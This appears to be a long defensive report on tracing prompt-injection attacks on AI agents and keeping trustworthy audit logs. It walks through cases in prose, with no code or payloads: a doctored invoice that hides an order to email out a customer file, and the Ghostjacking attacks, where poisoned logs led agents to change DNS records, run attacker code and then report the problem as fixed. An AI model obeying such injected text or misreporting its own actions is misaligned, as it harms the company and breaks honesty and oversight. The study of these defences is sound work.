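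NeuroTaint, a system by Cai and colleagues, keeps a record of each item's origin across sessions and compares texts by meaning as well as wording. If this finds no link between a suspect text and the harmful action, the system tests whether the action would still occur without that text. On the researchers' own benchmark of 400 scenarios, NeuroTaint found 93.5% of the real links, and 92.1% of the links it reported were real.

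Attribution methods score each passage in the input by how much it contributed to the output. *AttnTrace* (Wang, Geng and colleagues, 2025) calculates the score from attention weights, numbers inside a language model that determine how strongly each token draws on earlier ones. Only a few tokens in an influential passage have high weights, so AttnTrace averages only the highest ones. When several malicious passages push towards the same output, they can split the attention between them, which makes each look less important. To counter this, AttnTrace repeats the calculation on random subsets of the input. On one set of questions, 95% of the passages it flagged were malicious, and it found 95% of the malicious passages. It took about 10 seconds per case, while an earlier method took more than 100 seconds and scored 80% on both measures.

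Reading attention weights requires running the model and inspecting its internals, which customers of commercial models usually can't do. The researchers suggest using an open model as a stand-in, but the scores then describe how the open model processes the text, rather than how the original model did. Asking the original model to name its sources takes less work but is less reliable, because the injected text can include an instruction to name the wrong ones.

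Once a document is under suspicion, a narrower tool can help locate the injected text. *PromptLocate* (Jia, Liu and colleagues, 2025) splits a document into segments, identifies those that contain injected instructions, and then looks for the data that the attacker added with them. It could find the hidden line in the invoice, but it wouldn't show that the assistant had acted on that line.

A high score doesn't show that the influence was improper, either. Ahad, Hossain and colleagues (2026), in *Influence Is Not Authority*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to transfer money to Alice without supplying her account number. The agent looks the number up, so the tool's result strongly influences the transfer, even though the user authorised it. The researchers built 24 pairs of cases where the same authorised action took a necessary value either from the user or from a legitimate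 tool. They scored each source by removing it and measuring how much support the action lost. In all 24 pairs, moving the value to the tool made the action look more like an attack. On average, this move changed the score more than replacing the authorised action with an unauthorised one, such as a transfer to Mallory. An accounts assistant takes nearly every payment detail from outside documents, so an investigator who relied on such scores would get many false leads.

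### Removing the text and running again

The third family tests the cause directly by removing or replacing the suspect text and checking whether the agent still takes the same action. *AttriGuard* (2026) proposes a defence based on this test and argues that attackers can easily manipulate methods that judge an action by its plausibility. The doctored invoice, for instance, presents the theft of the customer file as routine record-keeping.

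*Causal Agent Replay* (Shah, 2026) extends the idea to every step of a run. In its example, a customer-support agent receives a message containing an injected order to issue a full refund. The agent looks up the purchase, decides to refund it, issues the refund and writes a polite confirmation. The blame belongs to the decision, one step before the call that issued the refund. Shah's software keeps everything before a chosen step unchanged, reruns the model from there many times, and counts how often the bad outcome returns.

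Shah picks the latest step at which deciding again still makes a clear difference to the outcome. After that step, the agent has committed itself to the refund. The size of the difference doesn't identify the responsible step, because rerunning the agent from an early, irrelevant step also reruns the decisive one. A failure can also require two steps in combination, so a second method divides the responsibility between them. Both methods gave the right answers when Shah tested them on small artificial systems with known causes, but this is weaker evidence than a test on real incidents.

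Reruns have practical limits. Hosted models give varying answers even with random sampling turned down to zero, because the provider's servers process requests in changing groups and tiny rounding differences add up. Rerunning the accounts assistant with its real tools would also send the customer file to the criminal again. Shah uses simulated tools and leaves tools with real side effects out of scope.

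Restoring the starting point exactly is also difficult. In *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual*, Pakhomov and Nijkamp (2026) saved 24 states of a simulated environment, restored each one five times and continued with fixed rules in place of a language model. The five copies always agreed with one another, but they differed from the original run in 9 of the 24 states when tools failed at random 5% of the time, and in 20 when tools failed 20% of the time. The saved states had left out the position in the sequence of random numbers that determined which calls failed. Restoring that position removed every difference. Comparing the copies only with each other would have missed the problem, so an investigator needs to replay the run without changing anything and compare the result with the original.

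Results vary further when the system includes a language model. In *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026) replayed AgentDojo attacks up to the point where the agent read the injected text, then let it continue from there several times. For the small model Qwen3-8B, the share of starting points that led to mixed results rose from 7% to 28% when the model wrote out its reasoning before answering. Across the reasoning agents tested, a second run of the same task gave a different result from the first up to 35% of the time.

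A single harmless rerun doesn't clear a document of suspicion. If the agent obeys the injection 30% of the time from a given starting point, five independent reruns would all be harmless about 17% of the time. At a rate of 1%, an investigator would need about 300 reruns for a 95% chance of seeing the attack at least once. Attacks succeed less often against well-trained models, so the ones that do succeed are harder to reproduce.

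Even a successful removal test can point to the wrong item. If the investigator removed the customer file from the accounts assistant's input, the theft would also stop, because there would be nothing to steal. The theft required the file, but the instruction came from the invoice. Yao and colleagues likewise argue that legitimate operations can affect the harmful action, so investigators still have to sort through the candidates that removal tests produce.

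### AgentTracer

In October 2026, Yao and colleagues published AgentTracer, a method for tracing attacks whose steps serve one purpose but pass no data to each other. In their example, a user asks an agent to download a software release from a website and upload it to a repository on GitHub, a code-hosting service. The release page contains an injected instruction. While continuing the user's task, the agent also registers the attacker's SSH key, fetches received emails, verifies the GitHub account and clears its working memory. The SSH key is a login credential, so it may give the attacker access to the repository.

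Suppose the company notices only that the agent cleared its memory. That call has no arguments, so a graph based on shared data can't connect it to the other steps. An attribution score might link it to the web page but wouldn't reveal the registered key. Finding the key is most urgent because the attacker could keep using it even if the company replaced all of the agent's own credentials.

AgentTracer first draws a graph of decisions. The starting point is the user's request, and every other point is something a successful tool call brought in or changed, such as a web page or a file. AgentTracer labels content that came from outside. Each arrow is an operation and runs from the item that led the agent to perform it to the item that resulted. To find what led to each decision, a language model reads the agent's written reasoning and extracts the sources, the intended operation and the expected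 result. AgentTracer then matches each of these to an actual tool call.

The second stage compares every call with the user's request. Requests are usually vague, so AgentTracer breaks them into steps and adds details from a prepared knowledge base. Yao and colleagues use the example of a request to summarise a payroll file if the total exceeds $1 million, and to send only the summary to a named auditor. The knowledge base adds that the agent may first locate and read the file. AgentTracer then makes three checks on each call:

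- **Action:** is the operation one that the user asked for, or a permitted supporting step?
- **Target:** does it affect only the files, people or accounts that the request covers?
- **Constraint:** does it respect the amounts, conditions and confirmations that apply?

AgentTracer marks a call as misaligned unless it passes every applicable check for at least one step of the task. For example, emailing the whole payroll file to the auditor would pass the check on the recipient but break the restriction on what to send.

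A user can also let a document supply missing details. "Pay the bill in bill.txt" authorises the file to provide the payee and the amount, but not to add new tasks. This distinction would help with the doctored invoice's instruction to email the customer file, which is a new task. The changed bank account is harder to catch because the user expects the invoice to contain the payment details. AgentTracer might well treat a payment to the criminal's account as authorised.

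The third stage traces the attack backwards. AgentTracer starts with a suspicious event, here the memory clearing, and searches the log for matching calls, newest first. For each match, it takes the part of the log between the preceding user request and the event, and discards failed calls. It then follows misaligned arrows back from the event until there are no more. If the trail ends at outside content, AgentTracer reports that content as the source and the log line where it entered as the injection point. If the trail ends elsewhere, AgentTracer doesn't label the event an injection, because the agent may have made a mistake.

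AgentTracer discards failed calls, which keeps steps that never took effect out of the graph. But this also prevents it from starting a trace at the accounts assistant's refused payment, which would have been the company's earliest warning.

### How well AgentTracer works

Yao and colleagues took 300 logs of successful attacks from each of two public test suites, AgentDyn and InjecAgent. They hid these among 1,800 user requests and 9,000 background tool calls from five months of normal use of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. AgentTracer identified the exact log line of the injection in 94.17% of cases. Of the calls it included in its reconstructed attacks, 93.56% belonged there. It recovered about 90% of the attack steps, but a missed step can matter a good deal if it registered a key.

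The background logs add less difficulty than their size suggests, because AgentTracer starts from a known suspicious event, which leads it almost directly to the right part of the log. In a separate sample of 100 attacks, having a language model analyse the whole history instead reduced accuracy in finding the injection point only from 91% to 89%, though it took 31% longer and used 51% more tokens. In practice, the hard part may be noticing the suspicious event, which the experiment did not test.

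The researchers compared AgentTracer with seven alternatives on another 100 attacks. Codex and OpenClaw, both general-purpose agents, read the logs directly. AuthGraph, AgentArmor and ARGUS are research systems designed mainly as defences. In the table, "steps found" is the share of the attack's calls that each method recovered, and "steps correct" is the share of each method's reported calls that belonged to the attack.

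| Method | Attacks detected | Injection point found | Steps found | Steps correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | 93% | 70% | 46% | 51% |
| OpenClaw | 89% | 69% | 45% | 50% |
| Agent-BOM | 52% | 43% | 51% | 46% |
| NeuroTaint | 98% | 40% | 48% | 91% |
| AuthGraph | 100% | 68% | 88% | 75% |
| AgentArmor | 99% | 76% | 94% | 54% |
| ARGUS | 95% | 70% | 80% | 67% |
| AgentTracer | 98% | 94% | 88% | 93% |

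Most methods could detect an attack but were much worse at locating its source. NeuroTaint detected 98% of attacks but found the injection point in only 40%. AgentArmor recovered more of the attack steps than AgentTracer, but nearly half the calls it reported were not part of the attack. The comparison probably favors AgentTracer somewhat, since AgentTracer's developers ran the tests and had to rebuild some of the other systems from published descriptions.

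In further tests on the separate sample of 100, replacing AgentTracer's graph with one that linked calls in chronological order cut injection-point accuracy from 91% to 74%, because the legitimate and malicious calls alternated. Replacing the structured comparison with a language model's direct judgement of each call cut it to 64%. An investigator who asks a chatbot whether each logged action looks right should expect a similar loss of accuracy.

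Yao and colleagues also checked 394 steps from runs without any attack. The agent had departed from the user's request in 25 of them. AgentTracer wrongly flagged 13 of the other 369 (3.5%). They didn't run the full backward trace on these logs, so they didn't measure how often AgentTracer would wrongly identify a harmless document as the source of an injected instruction.

The method assumes that the log contains the agent's reasoning, that the attacker can't alter the log or the user's original request, and that the attack produces tool calls. It therefore doesn't cover injections that only make the agent give its user a false answer, or malicious code that acts without making separate tool calls. The need for reasoning records also excludes some commercial models. *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, for example, couldn't obtain the reasoning text of Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash. The version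 linked by time, which was 74% accurate, gives a rough idea of how accurate the method would be without reasoning records.

### A citation that points nowhere

Some systems ask an agent to state which inputs it relied on for each action. An investigator could then look up the citation instead of reconstructing the path from the action back to its source. *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings* (Yun, Kim and colleagues, October 2026) tested how useful these citations are to someone who reads the log later.

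They used saved runs from AgentDojo's Banking suite, in which agents pay bills and manage accounts at a simulated bank. Before each tool call, the agent had to explain its action and list the identifiers of the inputs behind it. The researchers selected 64 cases without regard to whether an attack had succeeded. In each one they picked an action and one value in it, such as an account number, and asked three questions:

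1. Does the value appear in the user's genuine request?
2. Which earlier outside records contain it?
3. Which of those records did the agent cite?

In one case, an agent read a bill, sent money to the account number printed on it and cited "in-3". The log showed that the number appeared in the bill, which answers the second question. But "in-3" was only a label the software assigned during the run. Without a table showing that it stood for the result of the agent's first action, an investigator could only guess from the supplied evidence that it referred to the bill.

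Two language models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.6 Luna, acted as the investigator. In 28 of the 64 cases, the third question had no justified answer without the table, so the correct response was to say the evidence was insufficient. Sonnet did so twice. In the other 26 cases it named a source without support, and 22 of those answers happened to be right. Luna made 21 unsupported claims, and 12 were right.

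With the table, Sonnet gave supported, correct answers in 24 of the 28 cases and Luna in 21. But across all 64 cases, the number of answers that matched the full record rose only from 46 to 49 for Sonnet and from 43 to 49 for Luna. Especially for Sonnet, the table mainly replaced lucky guesses with findings that someone else could check. That matters because the 85% success rate at guessing might fall with a longer log. These were short banking tasks with few possible sources, and it would be easier to guess wrong if the agent had read 200 emails.

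Asking a second model wouldn't have solved the problem. In 11 of the cases without the table, both models gave the same unsupported but correct answer, so their agreement would have looked like confirmation. Even with the table, each model gave 15 answers out of 64 that the evidence didn't justify, while a simple program that matched text and looked up identifiers gave none. A company can therefore use ordinary software for these lookups and keep language models for questions that need interpretation. Any export of the log also has to include the table, which is easy to forget because it contains no message text.

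Yun and colleagues also tried to test for causes by removing a suspect input and rerunning the agent. Only one case met their conditions. They ran it twice unchanged and twice without the input. The harmful action didn't occur in any of the four runs, even with the input present, so the test couldn't show whether removing the input made a difference. Four runs were also far too few to test an attack that rarely works.

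### Present, cited or the cause

These studies separate three claims that an incident report can easily run together.

| Claim | Evidence needed | What remains open |
|---|---|---|
| The text was present | A saved copy or matching hash, dated before the action | Whether it affected the agent |
| The agent cited the text | A saved citation and a table linking it to the record | Whether the citation is true and complete |
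| The text caused the action | Repeated reruns with and without the text, with everything else unchanged | Whether the user had authorised the action |

Pakhomov and Nijkamp object to studies that assign causes to failures by reading finished transcripts, because reading can't distinguish a cause from something that happened alongside it. For example, in their own analysis of a set of agent attacks, responses from outside services carried 84.9% of the successful attacks, but the test's designers had put the attack in a service response in 84.6% of the tasks analyzed. The high share reflected the design of the test, and the data couldn't show whether service responses were more dangerous than local files.

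An agent may fail to cite the input that led to its action, or cite one that had no bearing on it. In a further 54 attacked runs, Yun and colleagues recorded four harmful incidents, all by GPT-5.4 mini on the same bill-paying task. In all four, the agent did not cite the input containing the attack as a basis for its first harmful action, although it had cited that input earlier in two of the runs. Four incidents are too few to establish a rate, but they show that an investigator shouldn't rule out a document because the agent didn't cite it.

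Sometimes the logs give strong evidence of what caused an action without a rerun. The address records@northfield-update.example appeared only in the hidden line of the accounts assistant's input, and a model is very unlikely to invent the same address by chance. The match is therefore almost as convincing as an experiment in showing where the recipient came from. This reasoning fails for a call that contains no distinctive value, such as clearing the memory, and for the payment of an ordinary bill whose details appear in several records.

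The proof the company needs depends on what it plans to do. To block an invoice, it needs only evidence that the invoice contains a hidden instruction, since no honest supplier needs one. To decide whether a new filter would have prevented the theft, it has to know whether the instruction caused the theft. Proof of the cause isn't enough to accuse the supplier, because someone else may have forged the email.

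Finding what caused an action also doesn't show that the action was justified. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a survey of agent tracing, that a false item in an agent's memory can cause an action without justifying it. An investigator may find that a note about Northfield's new bank account fully explains a payment, but must still check whether the note was true and who had the authority to change the account.

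### What written reasoning can establish

Many models write out their reasoning before they act. If the log keeps this text, it may be the only record of how the agent got from the invoice to the email, and AgentTracer depends on this record. The model also makes part of its decision while it reasons. In its banking runs, *The Window Is in the Reasoning* cut Qwen3-8B's reasoning short and let the model continue from that point several times. The first half of the reasoning settled 55% of the variation in outcome that remained when the model first read the injection, and the first 70% settled 62%.

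However, a reader can't always tell whether an agent will obey the injected instruction, even when its partial reasoning has already determined the outcome. The same researchers asked other language models to predict the outcome from that partial reasoning. Weaker models missed much of what the text had already determined, but stronger ones did much better.

A model's written reasoning can also omit what influenced it. *Faithfulness as Information Flow* (2026) describes how a misleading hint in a question can change a model's answer without appearing in its reasoning. Sometimes the model writes no reasoning at all. *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025) includes a GPT-5 run in which the agent clicked the attacker's button without explanation, possibly because the injected text had asked for brief narration. In another run, a different model wrote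 an explicit justification that described the injected button as a way to reveal more of the page.

Written reasoning can even contain invented events. In *Reasoning Models Confabulate to Defend Injected Beliefs About Their Own Requests* (2026), researchers planted the concept of an antibiotic in a small reasoning model that had been asked for a haiku about a quark. The model's reasoning described the user first asking about a quark and then correcting the request to antibiotics, but the user had made no correction. An investigator who had only the reasoning would conclude that the user had changed the task.

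An investigator can therefore use the reasoning to decide where to look and to prove what the model wrote before it acted, but needs to check its statements about events against other records. If the accounts assistant had written that Patel asked it to send out the customer file, the investigator could compare that claim with the saved request, "Deal with the new invoices", and see that it was false. An influence that the reasoning leaves out is harder to detect because there is no statement to check. The investigator would have to find it through a distinctive value in the call or through repeated reruns.

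## When can the log not be relied on?

An investigator who checks an agent's written reasoning against the log assumes that the log is right. But ordinary configuration mistakes can keep entries from reaching the log, and someone can change entries after they are recorded. Even a complete and accurate log can cause harm if another AI agent reads it, because it may contain text written by an attacker.

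### Gaps between services

Microsoft turns audit logging on by default for organisations that use Microsoft 365, its office software, according to Microsoft's *Audit log activities*. The records can still fail to reach security teams, many of which assume that default logging ensures they arrive. *What Your M365 Logs Are Not Telling You* (Graslie, 2026), a guide from the security training company SANS, explains that collection depends on settings in five separate places, each with its own administration page, access rights and way of failing. A mistake in one place produces no warning in the others.

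Security teams usually copy records from many services into a SIEM, a central system for searching logs and raising alerts. Microsoft divides its audit records into several feeds, and the collecting software has to request each one. AWS, which sells such a collector, lists separate feeds for the company directory, email and shared files, plus a general feed that includes Copilot's records. If nobody subscribes to the general feed, Copilot's records never reach the SIEM, though the email records still do. An investigator looking into an accounts assistant built on Copilot might then find the email that carried the customer file but no record that the assistant had opened an invoice first.

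Searching the wrong table has a similar effect. The widely available OfficeActivity table by default covers only about 40% of the activity in Microsoft's audit log, and Graslie warns that nothing in the data shows that the rest is missing. Another Microsoft table, for searching Copilot activity, returns no results unless the organisation has deployed a separate security product and enabled the right setting. An empty result may therefore mean either that Copilot did nothing or that nobody was collecting its records.

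Microsoft deliberately keeps the text of conversations out of its Copilot audit log for privacy and security, as Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* explains. Other omissions come from software faults. In 2025, Copilot could use a file without naming it in the audit record. A test in Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* confirmed that Microsoft later closed this gap.

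Graslie's guide includes commands that check whether the feeds and mailbox settings are active. A company should also test the whole path, because correct settings don't guarantee that a record arrives. An employee can ask the agent to open a harmless test document, then look for the matching entry in the central system. Repeating the test whenever the settings or product version change would catch many silent failures.

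Between tests, routine counts of log records can help reveal gaps. If the agent on a busy machine suddenly produces no records, somebody should find out why. The counts need to be separate for each feed and event type, since a total can look normal even when records of file reads have stopped.

### Products outside the customer's log

New agent products can reach customers before the logging for them is ready. In March 2026, Anthropic's *Use Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* warned that audit logs and data exports didn't capture activity in Cowork, the company's agent for office work. The Compliance API, which customers' security software uses to collect records from Anthropic, didn't capture it either. Conversation histories stayed on users' own computers. Anthropic told customers who needed audit trails for compliance not to enable Cowork for regulated work.

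Anthropic has since closed much of this gap for customers on its Enterprise plan. Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* announced that the API would supply prompts, responses and tool calls from Cowork and from some versions of Claude Code, the company's coding agent. The table draws on that announcement, on the coverage listed in Anthropic's *Get started with Claude Compliance API integrations* as of late November 2026, and on a July 2026 OpenAI help page about the Atlas browser.

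| Product | What the customer could collect through the compliance interface |
|---|---|
| Cowork, Enterprise plan | Prompts, responses and tool calls |
| Claude Code in the desktop app or at the command line, Enterprise plan | Prompts, responses and tool calls |
| Claude Code on the web | Nothing when Anthropic announced the extension |
| Cowork or Claude Code run through Amazon's, Google's or Microsoft's cloud | Nothing when Anthropic announced the extension |
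| Claude Platform, for companies that build their own agents | Administrative changes and file activity, but no prompts or responses |
| OpenAI's Atlas browser | Nothing in July 2026 |

OpenAI also warned that companies' retention and deletion rules might not cover the activity of Atlas's agent. In *New compliance and administrative tools for ChatGPT Enterprise* (2024), OpenAI promises to keep adding log types to match its products, so a customer can't assume that the logs will cover a new feature on the day it appears.

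A company that built the accounts assistant on the Claude Platform could export a record of who created the access key, but not the invoice text or the order to send the email. It would have to record those itself, which it can do because its own software runs the loop around the model. Turning on the provider's log after an incident wouldn't show what happened, because the log only covers activity after the customer enables it, according to Anthropic's *Audit Claude Platform activity with the Compliance API* (2026).

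Where an agent runs also affects what the customer can see. Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* lists web and mobile versions of Cowork and an option to run it in the cloud. When an agent on an employee's laptop opens a web page, the connection normally crosses the company's network, where a firewall can record it. When the agent runs on the provider's servers, those servers open the page, so the company's firewall may record only that the employee connected to the provider. A script on the laptop, like the one Elastic wrote, would also miss the visit.

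Records kept by the systems an agent acts on can fill some of these gaps. For example, the company's mail service records each email sent from the company's account, wherever the agent runs. Earlier, the investigator used message number M-90417 to trace one email to one run. Software can make the same comparison every night for every message the agent's account sent, and list those with no matching tool call. This only works if the agent has its own account, because otherwise its messages mix with the employee's. It also can't detect actions that leave no record at the destination, such as reading a stranger's web page.

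Some products offer a second source of records. According to Anthropic's *Making Claude Cowork ready for enterprise*, the Cowork application can send OpenTelemetry events to a customer's SIEM, with an identifier that links them to the Compliance API's records. If no source covers a product, the safest course is to keep it away from work that needs an audit trail, as Anthropic recommended for Cowork in March.

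### Who should write the record

The log can't be relied on when the model writes it. An injection that gets an agent to email out a customer file can also include an instruction to omit the email from the log, or to describe it as an update that the user requested. Even an honest model can log something false, because it lacks some of the facts. For example, if it writes its log entry along with its request, it could record a payment that a policy check then refuses.

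The component that executes the call avoids these problems because it has the exact arguments, the account and permission used, and the result. In *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models*, Ojewale, Suresh and Venkatasubramanian (2026) do this logging with emitters, small pieces of code that attach to existing software and write records in a fixed format. Similarly, the Cowork application itself records whether a person approved each action or the software approved it automatically, which a model could easily misreport. The model's own explanation is still worth saving, as long as the log labels it as the model's statement.

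The log is also unreliable if the agent can change it. A coding agent that runs commands under a developer's account can edit any file the developer can, including a log on the same laptop. The recording software should therefore run under a different account and immediately send each record to another machine. The account that sends the records needs permission to add them, but not to read, change or delete them.

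A single entry in a log of tool calls can cover a lot of unrecorded activity. If an agent runs a program, the log shows the command but not what the program then does, which may include reading hundreds of files and contacting an outside server. Seeing those steps requires records from the operating system or the network as well.

The company also has to decide what happens when logging fails. For a high-risk action, the software can send the record first and act only after the log server confirms receipt, but then a fault in the log server stops the company's payments. For a routine file search, it may be better to continue, hold the record on the local machine and send it later.

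### Detecting changes with a hash chain

An intruder on the log server, or an administrator with something to hide, may try to rewrite the records. Append-only storage makes this harder because it allows new records to be added but prevents old ones from being changed or deleted, often for a fixed period. Ojewale and colleagues suggest a managed database with these restrictions, or plain files with extra protection. OpenAI exports compliance data for ChatGPT's business customers as log files that can't be changed, each covering a set period.

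Storage settings depend on whoever administers the storage, so many designs add a hash chain, which lets someone else detect a change. Each record gets a hash that depends on its own text and on the hash before it:

h_i = H(h_(i−1) || r_i)

Here r_i is the text of record i, || means joining two texts end to end, and H is the hash function. The first record has no predecessor, so the chain begins with a fixed value, h_0. With a modern function such as SHA-256, nobody knows a practical way to find a different text with the same hash.

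Suppose the log holds three records from the accounts assistant's run, and an insider later tries to hide the leak by changing the recipient in the second record to an address inside the company. The hashes below are invented and much shorter than real ones.

| Record | Original text | Original hash | Hash after the insider recalculates |
|---|---|---|---|
| r_1 | Read invoice 2291 | 4be1 | 4be1 |
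| r_2 | Sent customers.xlsx to an outside address | 90c7 | d25a |
| r_3 | Refused payment of £1,840 | 17fe | 6b03 |

If someone changes only the text of the second record, a checking program calculates the hash d25a, finds 90c7 stored there and reports a mismatch. If they also replace the stored hash, the mismatch moves to the third record, whose hash was calculated from 90c7. But if they then replace the third hash with 6b03, every record matches again. Replacing the hashes of millions of records this way would take an ordinary computer only minutes.

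The chain therefore protects the log only if someone outside the insider's control holds a copy of the latest hash. An auditor who received 17fe on the day would see that the log now ends in 6b03. The auditor doesn't need access to the records until there is a dispute, and a SHA-256 hash is only 32 bytes. Ojewale and colleagues call storing the hash outside the insider's control "anchoring", and suggest outside services that timestamp or publish hashes.

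The outside copy also reveals deletions at the end of the log. If the insider removed the third record, the first two would still form a valid chain, and only the auditor's copy of 17fe would show that another record had followed them. Records newer than the last anchor don't have this protection. If the company sends out a hash hourly, on the hour, an intruder at 09:50 can rewrite everything since 09:00 without causing a mismatch.

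Anchoring reveals that a record changed but can't restore the original, so the company also needs a copy of the log in a separate place.

### A working example and its limits

Ojewale and colleagues built a small open-source Python library, llm-audit-trail, to demonstrate the design. One component records the stages of training a model, and another records requests to a running model and its responses, mostly as hashes. A third lets staff enter approvals, exceptions and formal statements from the command line. All three write to one file, one record per line. The hash chain uses SHA-256 and starts from the fixed word "GENESIS". A checking function recalculates every hash, then reports how many records it examined and where the first mismatch occurred.

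The library shows that a hash chain takes little code to add and that human decisions can be recorded in the same timeline as technical events. Replaying the chain reveals a careless edit to one record. But anyone who can rewrite the whole file can produce a valid chain, because the library doesn't sign its records or send hashes to an outside service. Replay therefore can't confirm that nobody has altered or shortened the log, although the paper describes it as a way to do so. The paper recommends adding both safeguards for stronger deployments. It reports no measurements of the library's speed and no trial against a deliberate forger.

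The design also records a model's life cycle, from training data to deployment, in more detail than an agent's work on a task. Its standard fields identify the model, the dataset and the deployment, but not the run, the tool or the source of what the agent read. The company could use it to find out which version of the accounts assistant was live on 1 December and who had approved it. The company would have to add the missing fields to trace the email to the invoice.

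When a company buys its agent from a provider, part of the evidence is in the provider's log, which the provider may not want to share. Ojewale and colleagues propose that the provider publish a signed pointer, which identifies a record and includes a few harmless details, such as the model's version and the hashes of relevant files. In a later dispute, the customer could check that the record the provider produced was the one the pointer identified.

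Even a perfectly anchored chain can't show that a record was true when software wrote it. If the accounts assistant had written its own log and described the email as Patel's request, the chain would have preserved that false description. The chain also can't show that every event was recorded. Ojewale and colleagues acknowledge this when they call the timeline complete only "relative to the stored log". If the recording program crashes and stays down for an hour, the next record links to the last one before the crash, and every hash matches.

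Numbering the calls before they reach the log can expose such a gap. In the accounts assistant's run, the software assigned the identifiers C-03 to C-06 in order, so a log that jumped from C-04 to C-06 would show that a call was missing. Numbering wouldn't catch an action that bypassed the numbering software.

A log's timestamps can also be wrong. If an auditor receives a hash at 10:00, the records it covers must have existed by then, but a record marked 09:14 could have been written at 09:55. To settle a dispute about whether an approval came before a payment, the company would need to have sent the auditor hashes frequently, or to have times from a second clock, such as the bank's.

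### Log entries that carry an attack

Firewalls, mail servers and error trackers record what strangers send them, so their logs often contain an attacker's exact words. A person can read those words as evidence, but an AI agent that reads the log may follow them as instructions, just as it may follow a hidden line in an invoice.

This has become a practical problem because companies increasingly use agents to read logs. *Poisoning the SOC*, a poster by Seymour of Salesforce at the hacker conference DEF CON in August 2026, describes security teams adding agents to every stage of their work, from sorting alerts to responding without human involvement. Attackers write a large part of what these agents read. As a result, Seymour says, an agent might dismiss a real attack, chase a false one, fail to reach any conclusion or call tools on the attacker's behalf.

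Tenet Security, a start-up that sells protection against rogue agents, demonstrated the last of these at the same conference and calls it Ghostjacking. The target was a company using Cloudflare, a service that filters and routes website traffic. SecurityWeek's *‘Ghostjacking’ Attack Uses Poisoned Logs to Turn AI Agents Bad* reports that Cloudflare's firewall correctly blocked a malicious request and copied it word for word into its log. When an analyst asked an AI agent to review the event, the agent followed the instructions in the logged text and changed the company's DNS records, which tell browsers and mail servers where to send traffic for a domain. The new records pointed to a domain the attacker controlled, and the agent reported the issue as resolved.

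Coker (2026) reports in *“Ghostjacking” Exploits AI Agents’ Trusted Access to Evade Firewall Controls* that the attack worked in nine of ten attempts against Claude Code on the setup that Cloudflare recommends. SC Media's *‘GhostJacking’ attack turns error logs into indirect prompt injections* reports that Claude Code was running the Sonnet 4.6 model and that Tenet's demonstration used a different agent, Cursor. Ten attempts are enough to show that the attack is practical, but the true success rate could be anywhere from about 55% to nearly 100%. Sonnet 4.6 is several releases old, and newer models may resist the attack better.

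Claims about how many companies are exposed should be treated with more caution. Tenet estimates that half of Fortune 500 companies are vulnerable, Coker reports. That is close to the share that use Cloudflare (42%) or the monitoring service Datadog (48%), which Tenet also attacked. But a company that uses Cloudflare is exposed to the DNS attack only if it has an agent that can read the firewall's log and change the company's settings. SC Media reports that Tenet found 48 organisations with a potentially susceptible Cloudflare setup, including six confirmed members of the Fortune 500.

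In the Datadog attack, a false alert led Claude Code to run the attacker's code and leak cloud credentials. A third attack passed through two agents. Seer, the AI agent of the error-tracking service Sentry, read a false error report and repeated the attacker's proposed fix as its own finding. A coding agent acted on that finding and ran the attacker's code. It had received the fix as Seer's analysis, with no sign that the text came from an untrusted report. An agent's summary of untrusted content therefore needs the same label as the content itself.

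A hash chain would not have helped in the Cloudflare case, because the poisoned entry was an accurate, unaltered copy of what the attacker had sent. The agent's false report shows the risk of letting the model write its own record. That record would have ended with the issue marked as resolved, while a record from the software that executed the call would have shown the new DNS settings.

### Letting agents read logs safely

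Each log entry mixes text from different sources. In a firewall's entry, the time, the rule and the decision to block come from the firewall, while the content of the request comes from whoever sent it. Software can show an agent only the firewall's fields, which are enough for counting attacks or finding the rule that is triggered most often. When the content matters, a model with no tools can read it and choose one of a few fixed labels, such as "scan" or "login attempt". An attacker might still trick the model into choosing the wrong label, but can't use the label to pass an instruction to the agent. Filtering should apply only to the copy the agent sees, because a later investigator will need the original words.

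Telling the agent to ignore instructions in logs is a much weaker protection. *The firewall blocked the attack* (Churchill, 2026) quotes Steve Wilson, who co-leads a widely used list of security risks for language models, as calling security rules in prompts "suggestions to the model". Tenet's free protective tool includes such an instruction, but it also cuts off outside connections by default, blocks access to credentials and requires a person to approve every command.

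The more reliable remedy is to let the agent that reads the log propose changes but not approve them. This also suits other high-risk actions. In Tenet's scenario, the agent could still read the blocked request and draft a new DNS record, but software outside the model would hold the draft until a separate check or a person approved it. IANS's *'Ghostjacking' Shows How Attackers Can Turn Trusted Data Into AI Commands* (2026) similarly recommends that agents reading logs and alerts have read-only access and their own identity with minimal permissions. An agent that helps investigate the accounts assistant will read the invoice's hidden line, so it also shouldn't be able to send email or make payments.

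Reviewers should see the original log entry beside each proposal. Otherwise they have only the agent's summary, which may describe the attacker's request as a sensible repair, as Seer's did.

An agent with read-only access can still reach a false conclusion, and an attacker may only want it to dismiss an alert. Checking a sample of the agent's decisions offers limited protection. If the agent dismisses 500 events a day and a person rechecks 20 at random, the chance of rechecking the one that matters is 4%. Fixed rules are better for the few events that always deserve attention. For example, a simple program can alert a person to every DNS change, whatever the agent concluded about it.

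## Which actions are high-risk, and how can they be blocked or narrowed?

If a company required a second check on every action an agent takes, as it might for a DNS change, it would lose most of the benefit of using an agent. So it has to decide in advance which actions are dangerous, and choose limits that still work when the agent is following an attacker's instructions.

### Five tests

An action is high-risk if it fails any one of these tests.

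| Test | Passes | Fails |
|---|---|---|
| Can the company undo it? | Moving an email to a folder | Deleting the only copy of a contract |
| Is the result invisible to outsiders? | Saving a draft | Emailing a supplier |
| Does it leave private data alone? | Reading a public price list | Opening the customer file |
| Does it avoid spending money or promising to? | Listing unpaid bills | Paying a bill |
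| Does it leave permissions and memory unchanged? | Looking up a supplier | Adding a supplier's bank account, or saving a note for later sessions |

The outsider test covers more than sending messages. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, a help page about a high-security setting for ChatGPT, advises administrators not to enable actions that change data, even in trusted apps, unless they can confirm that an attacker couldn't see the effect. For instance, if the AI edits a document that a supplier can open, the supplier can read what it wrote, just as they could in an email.

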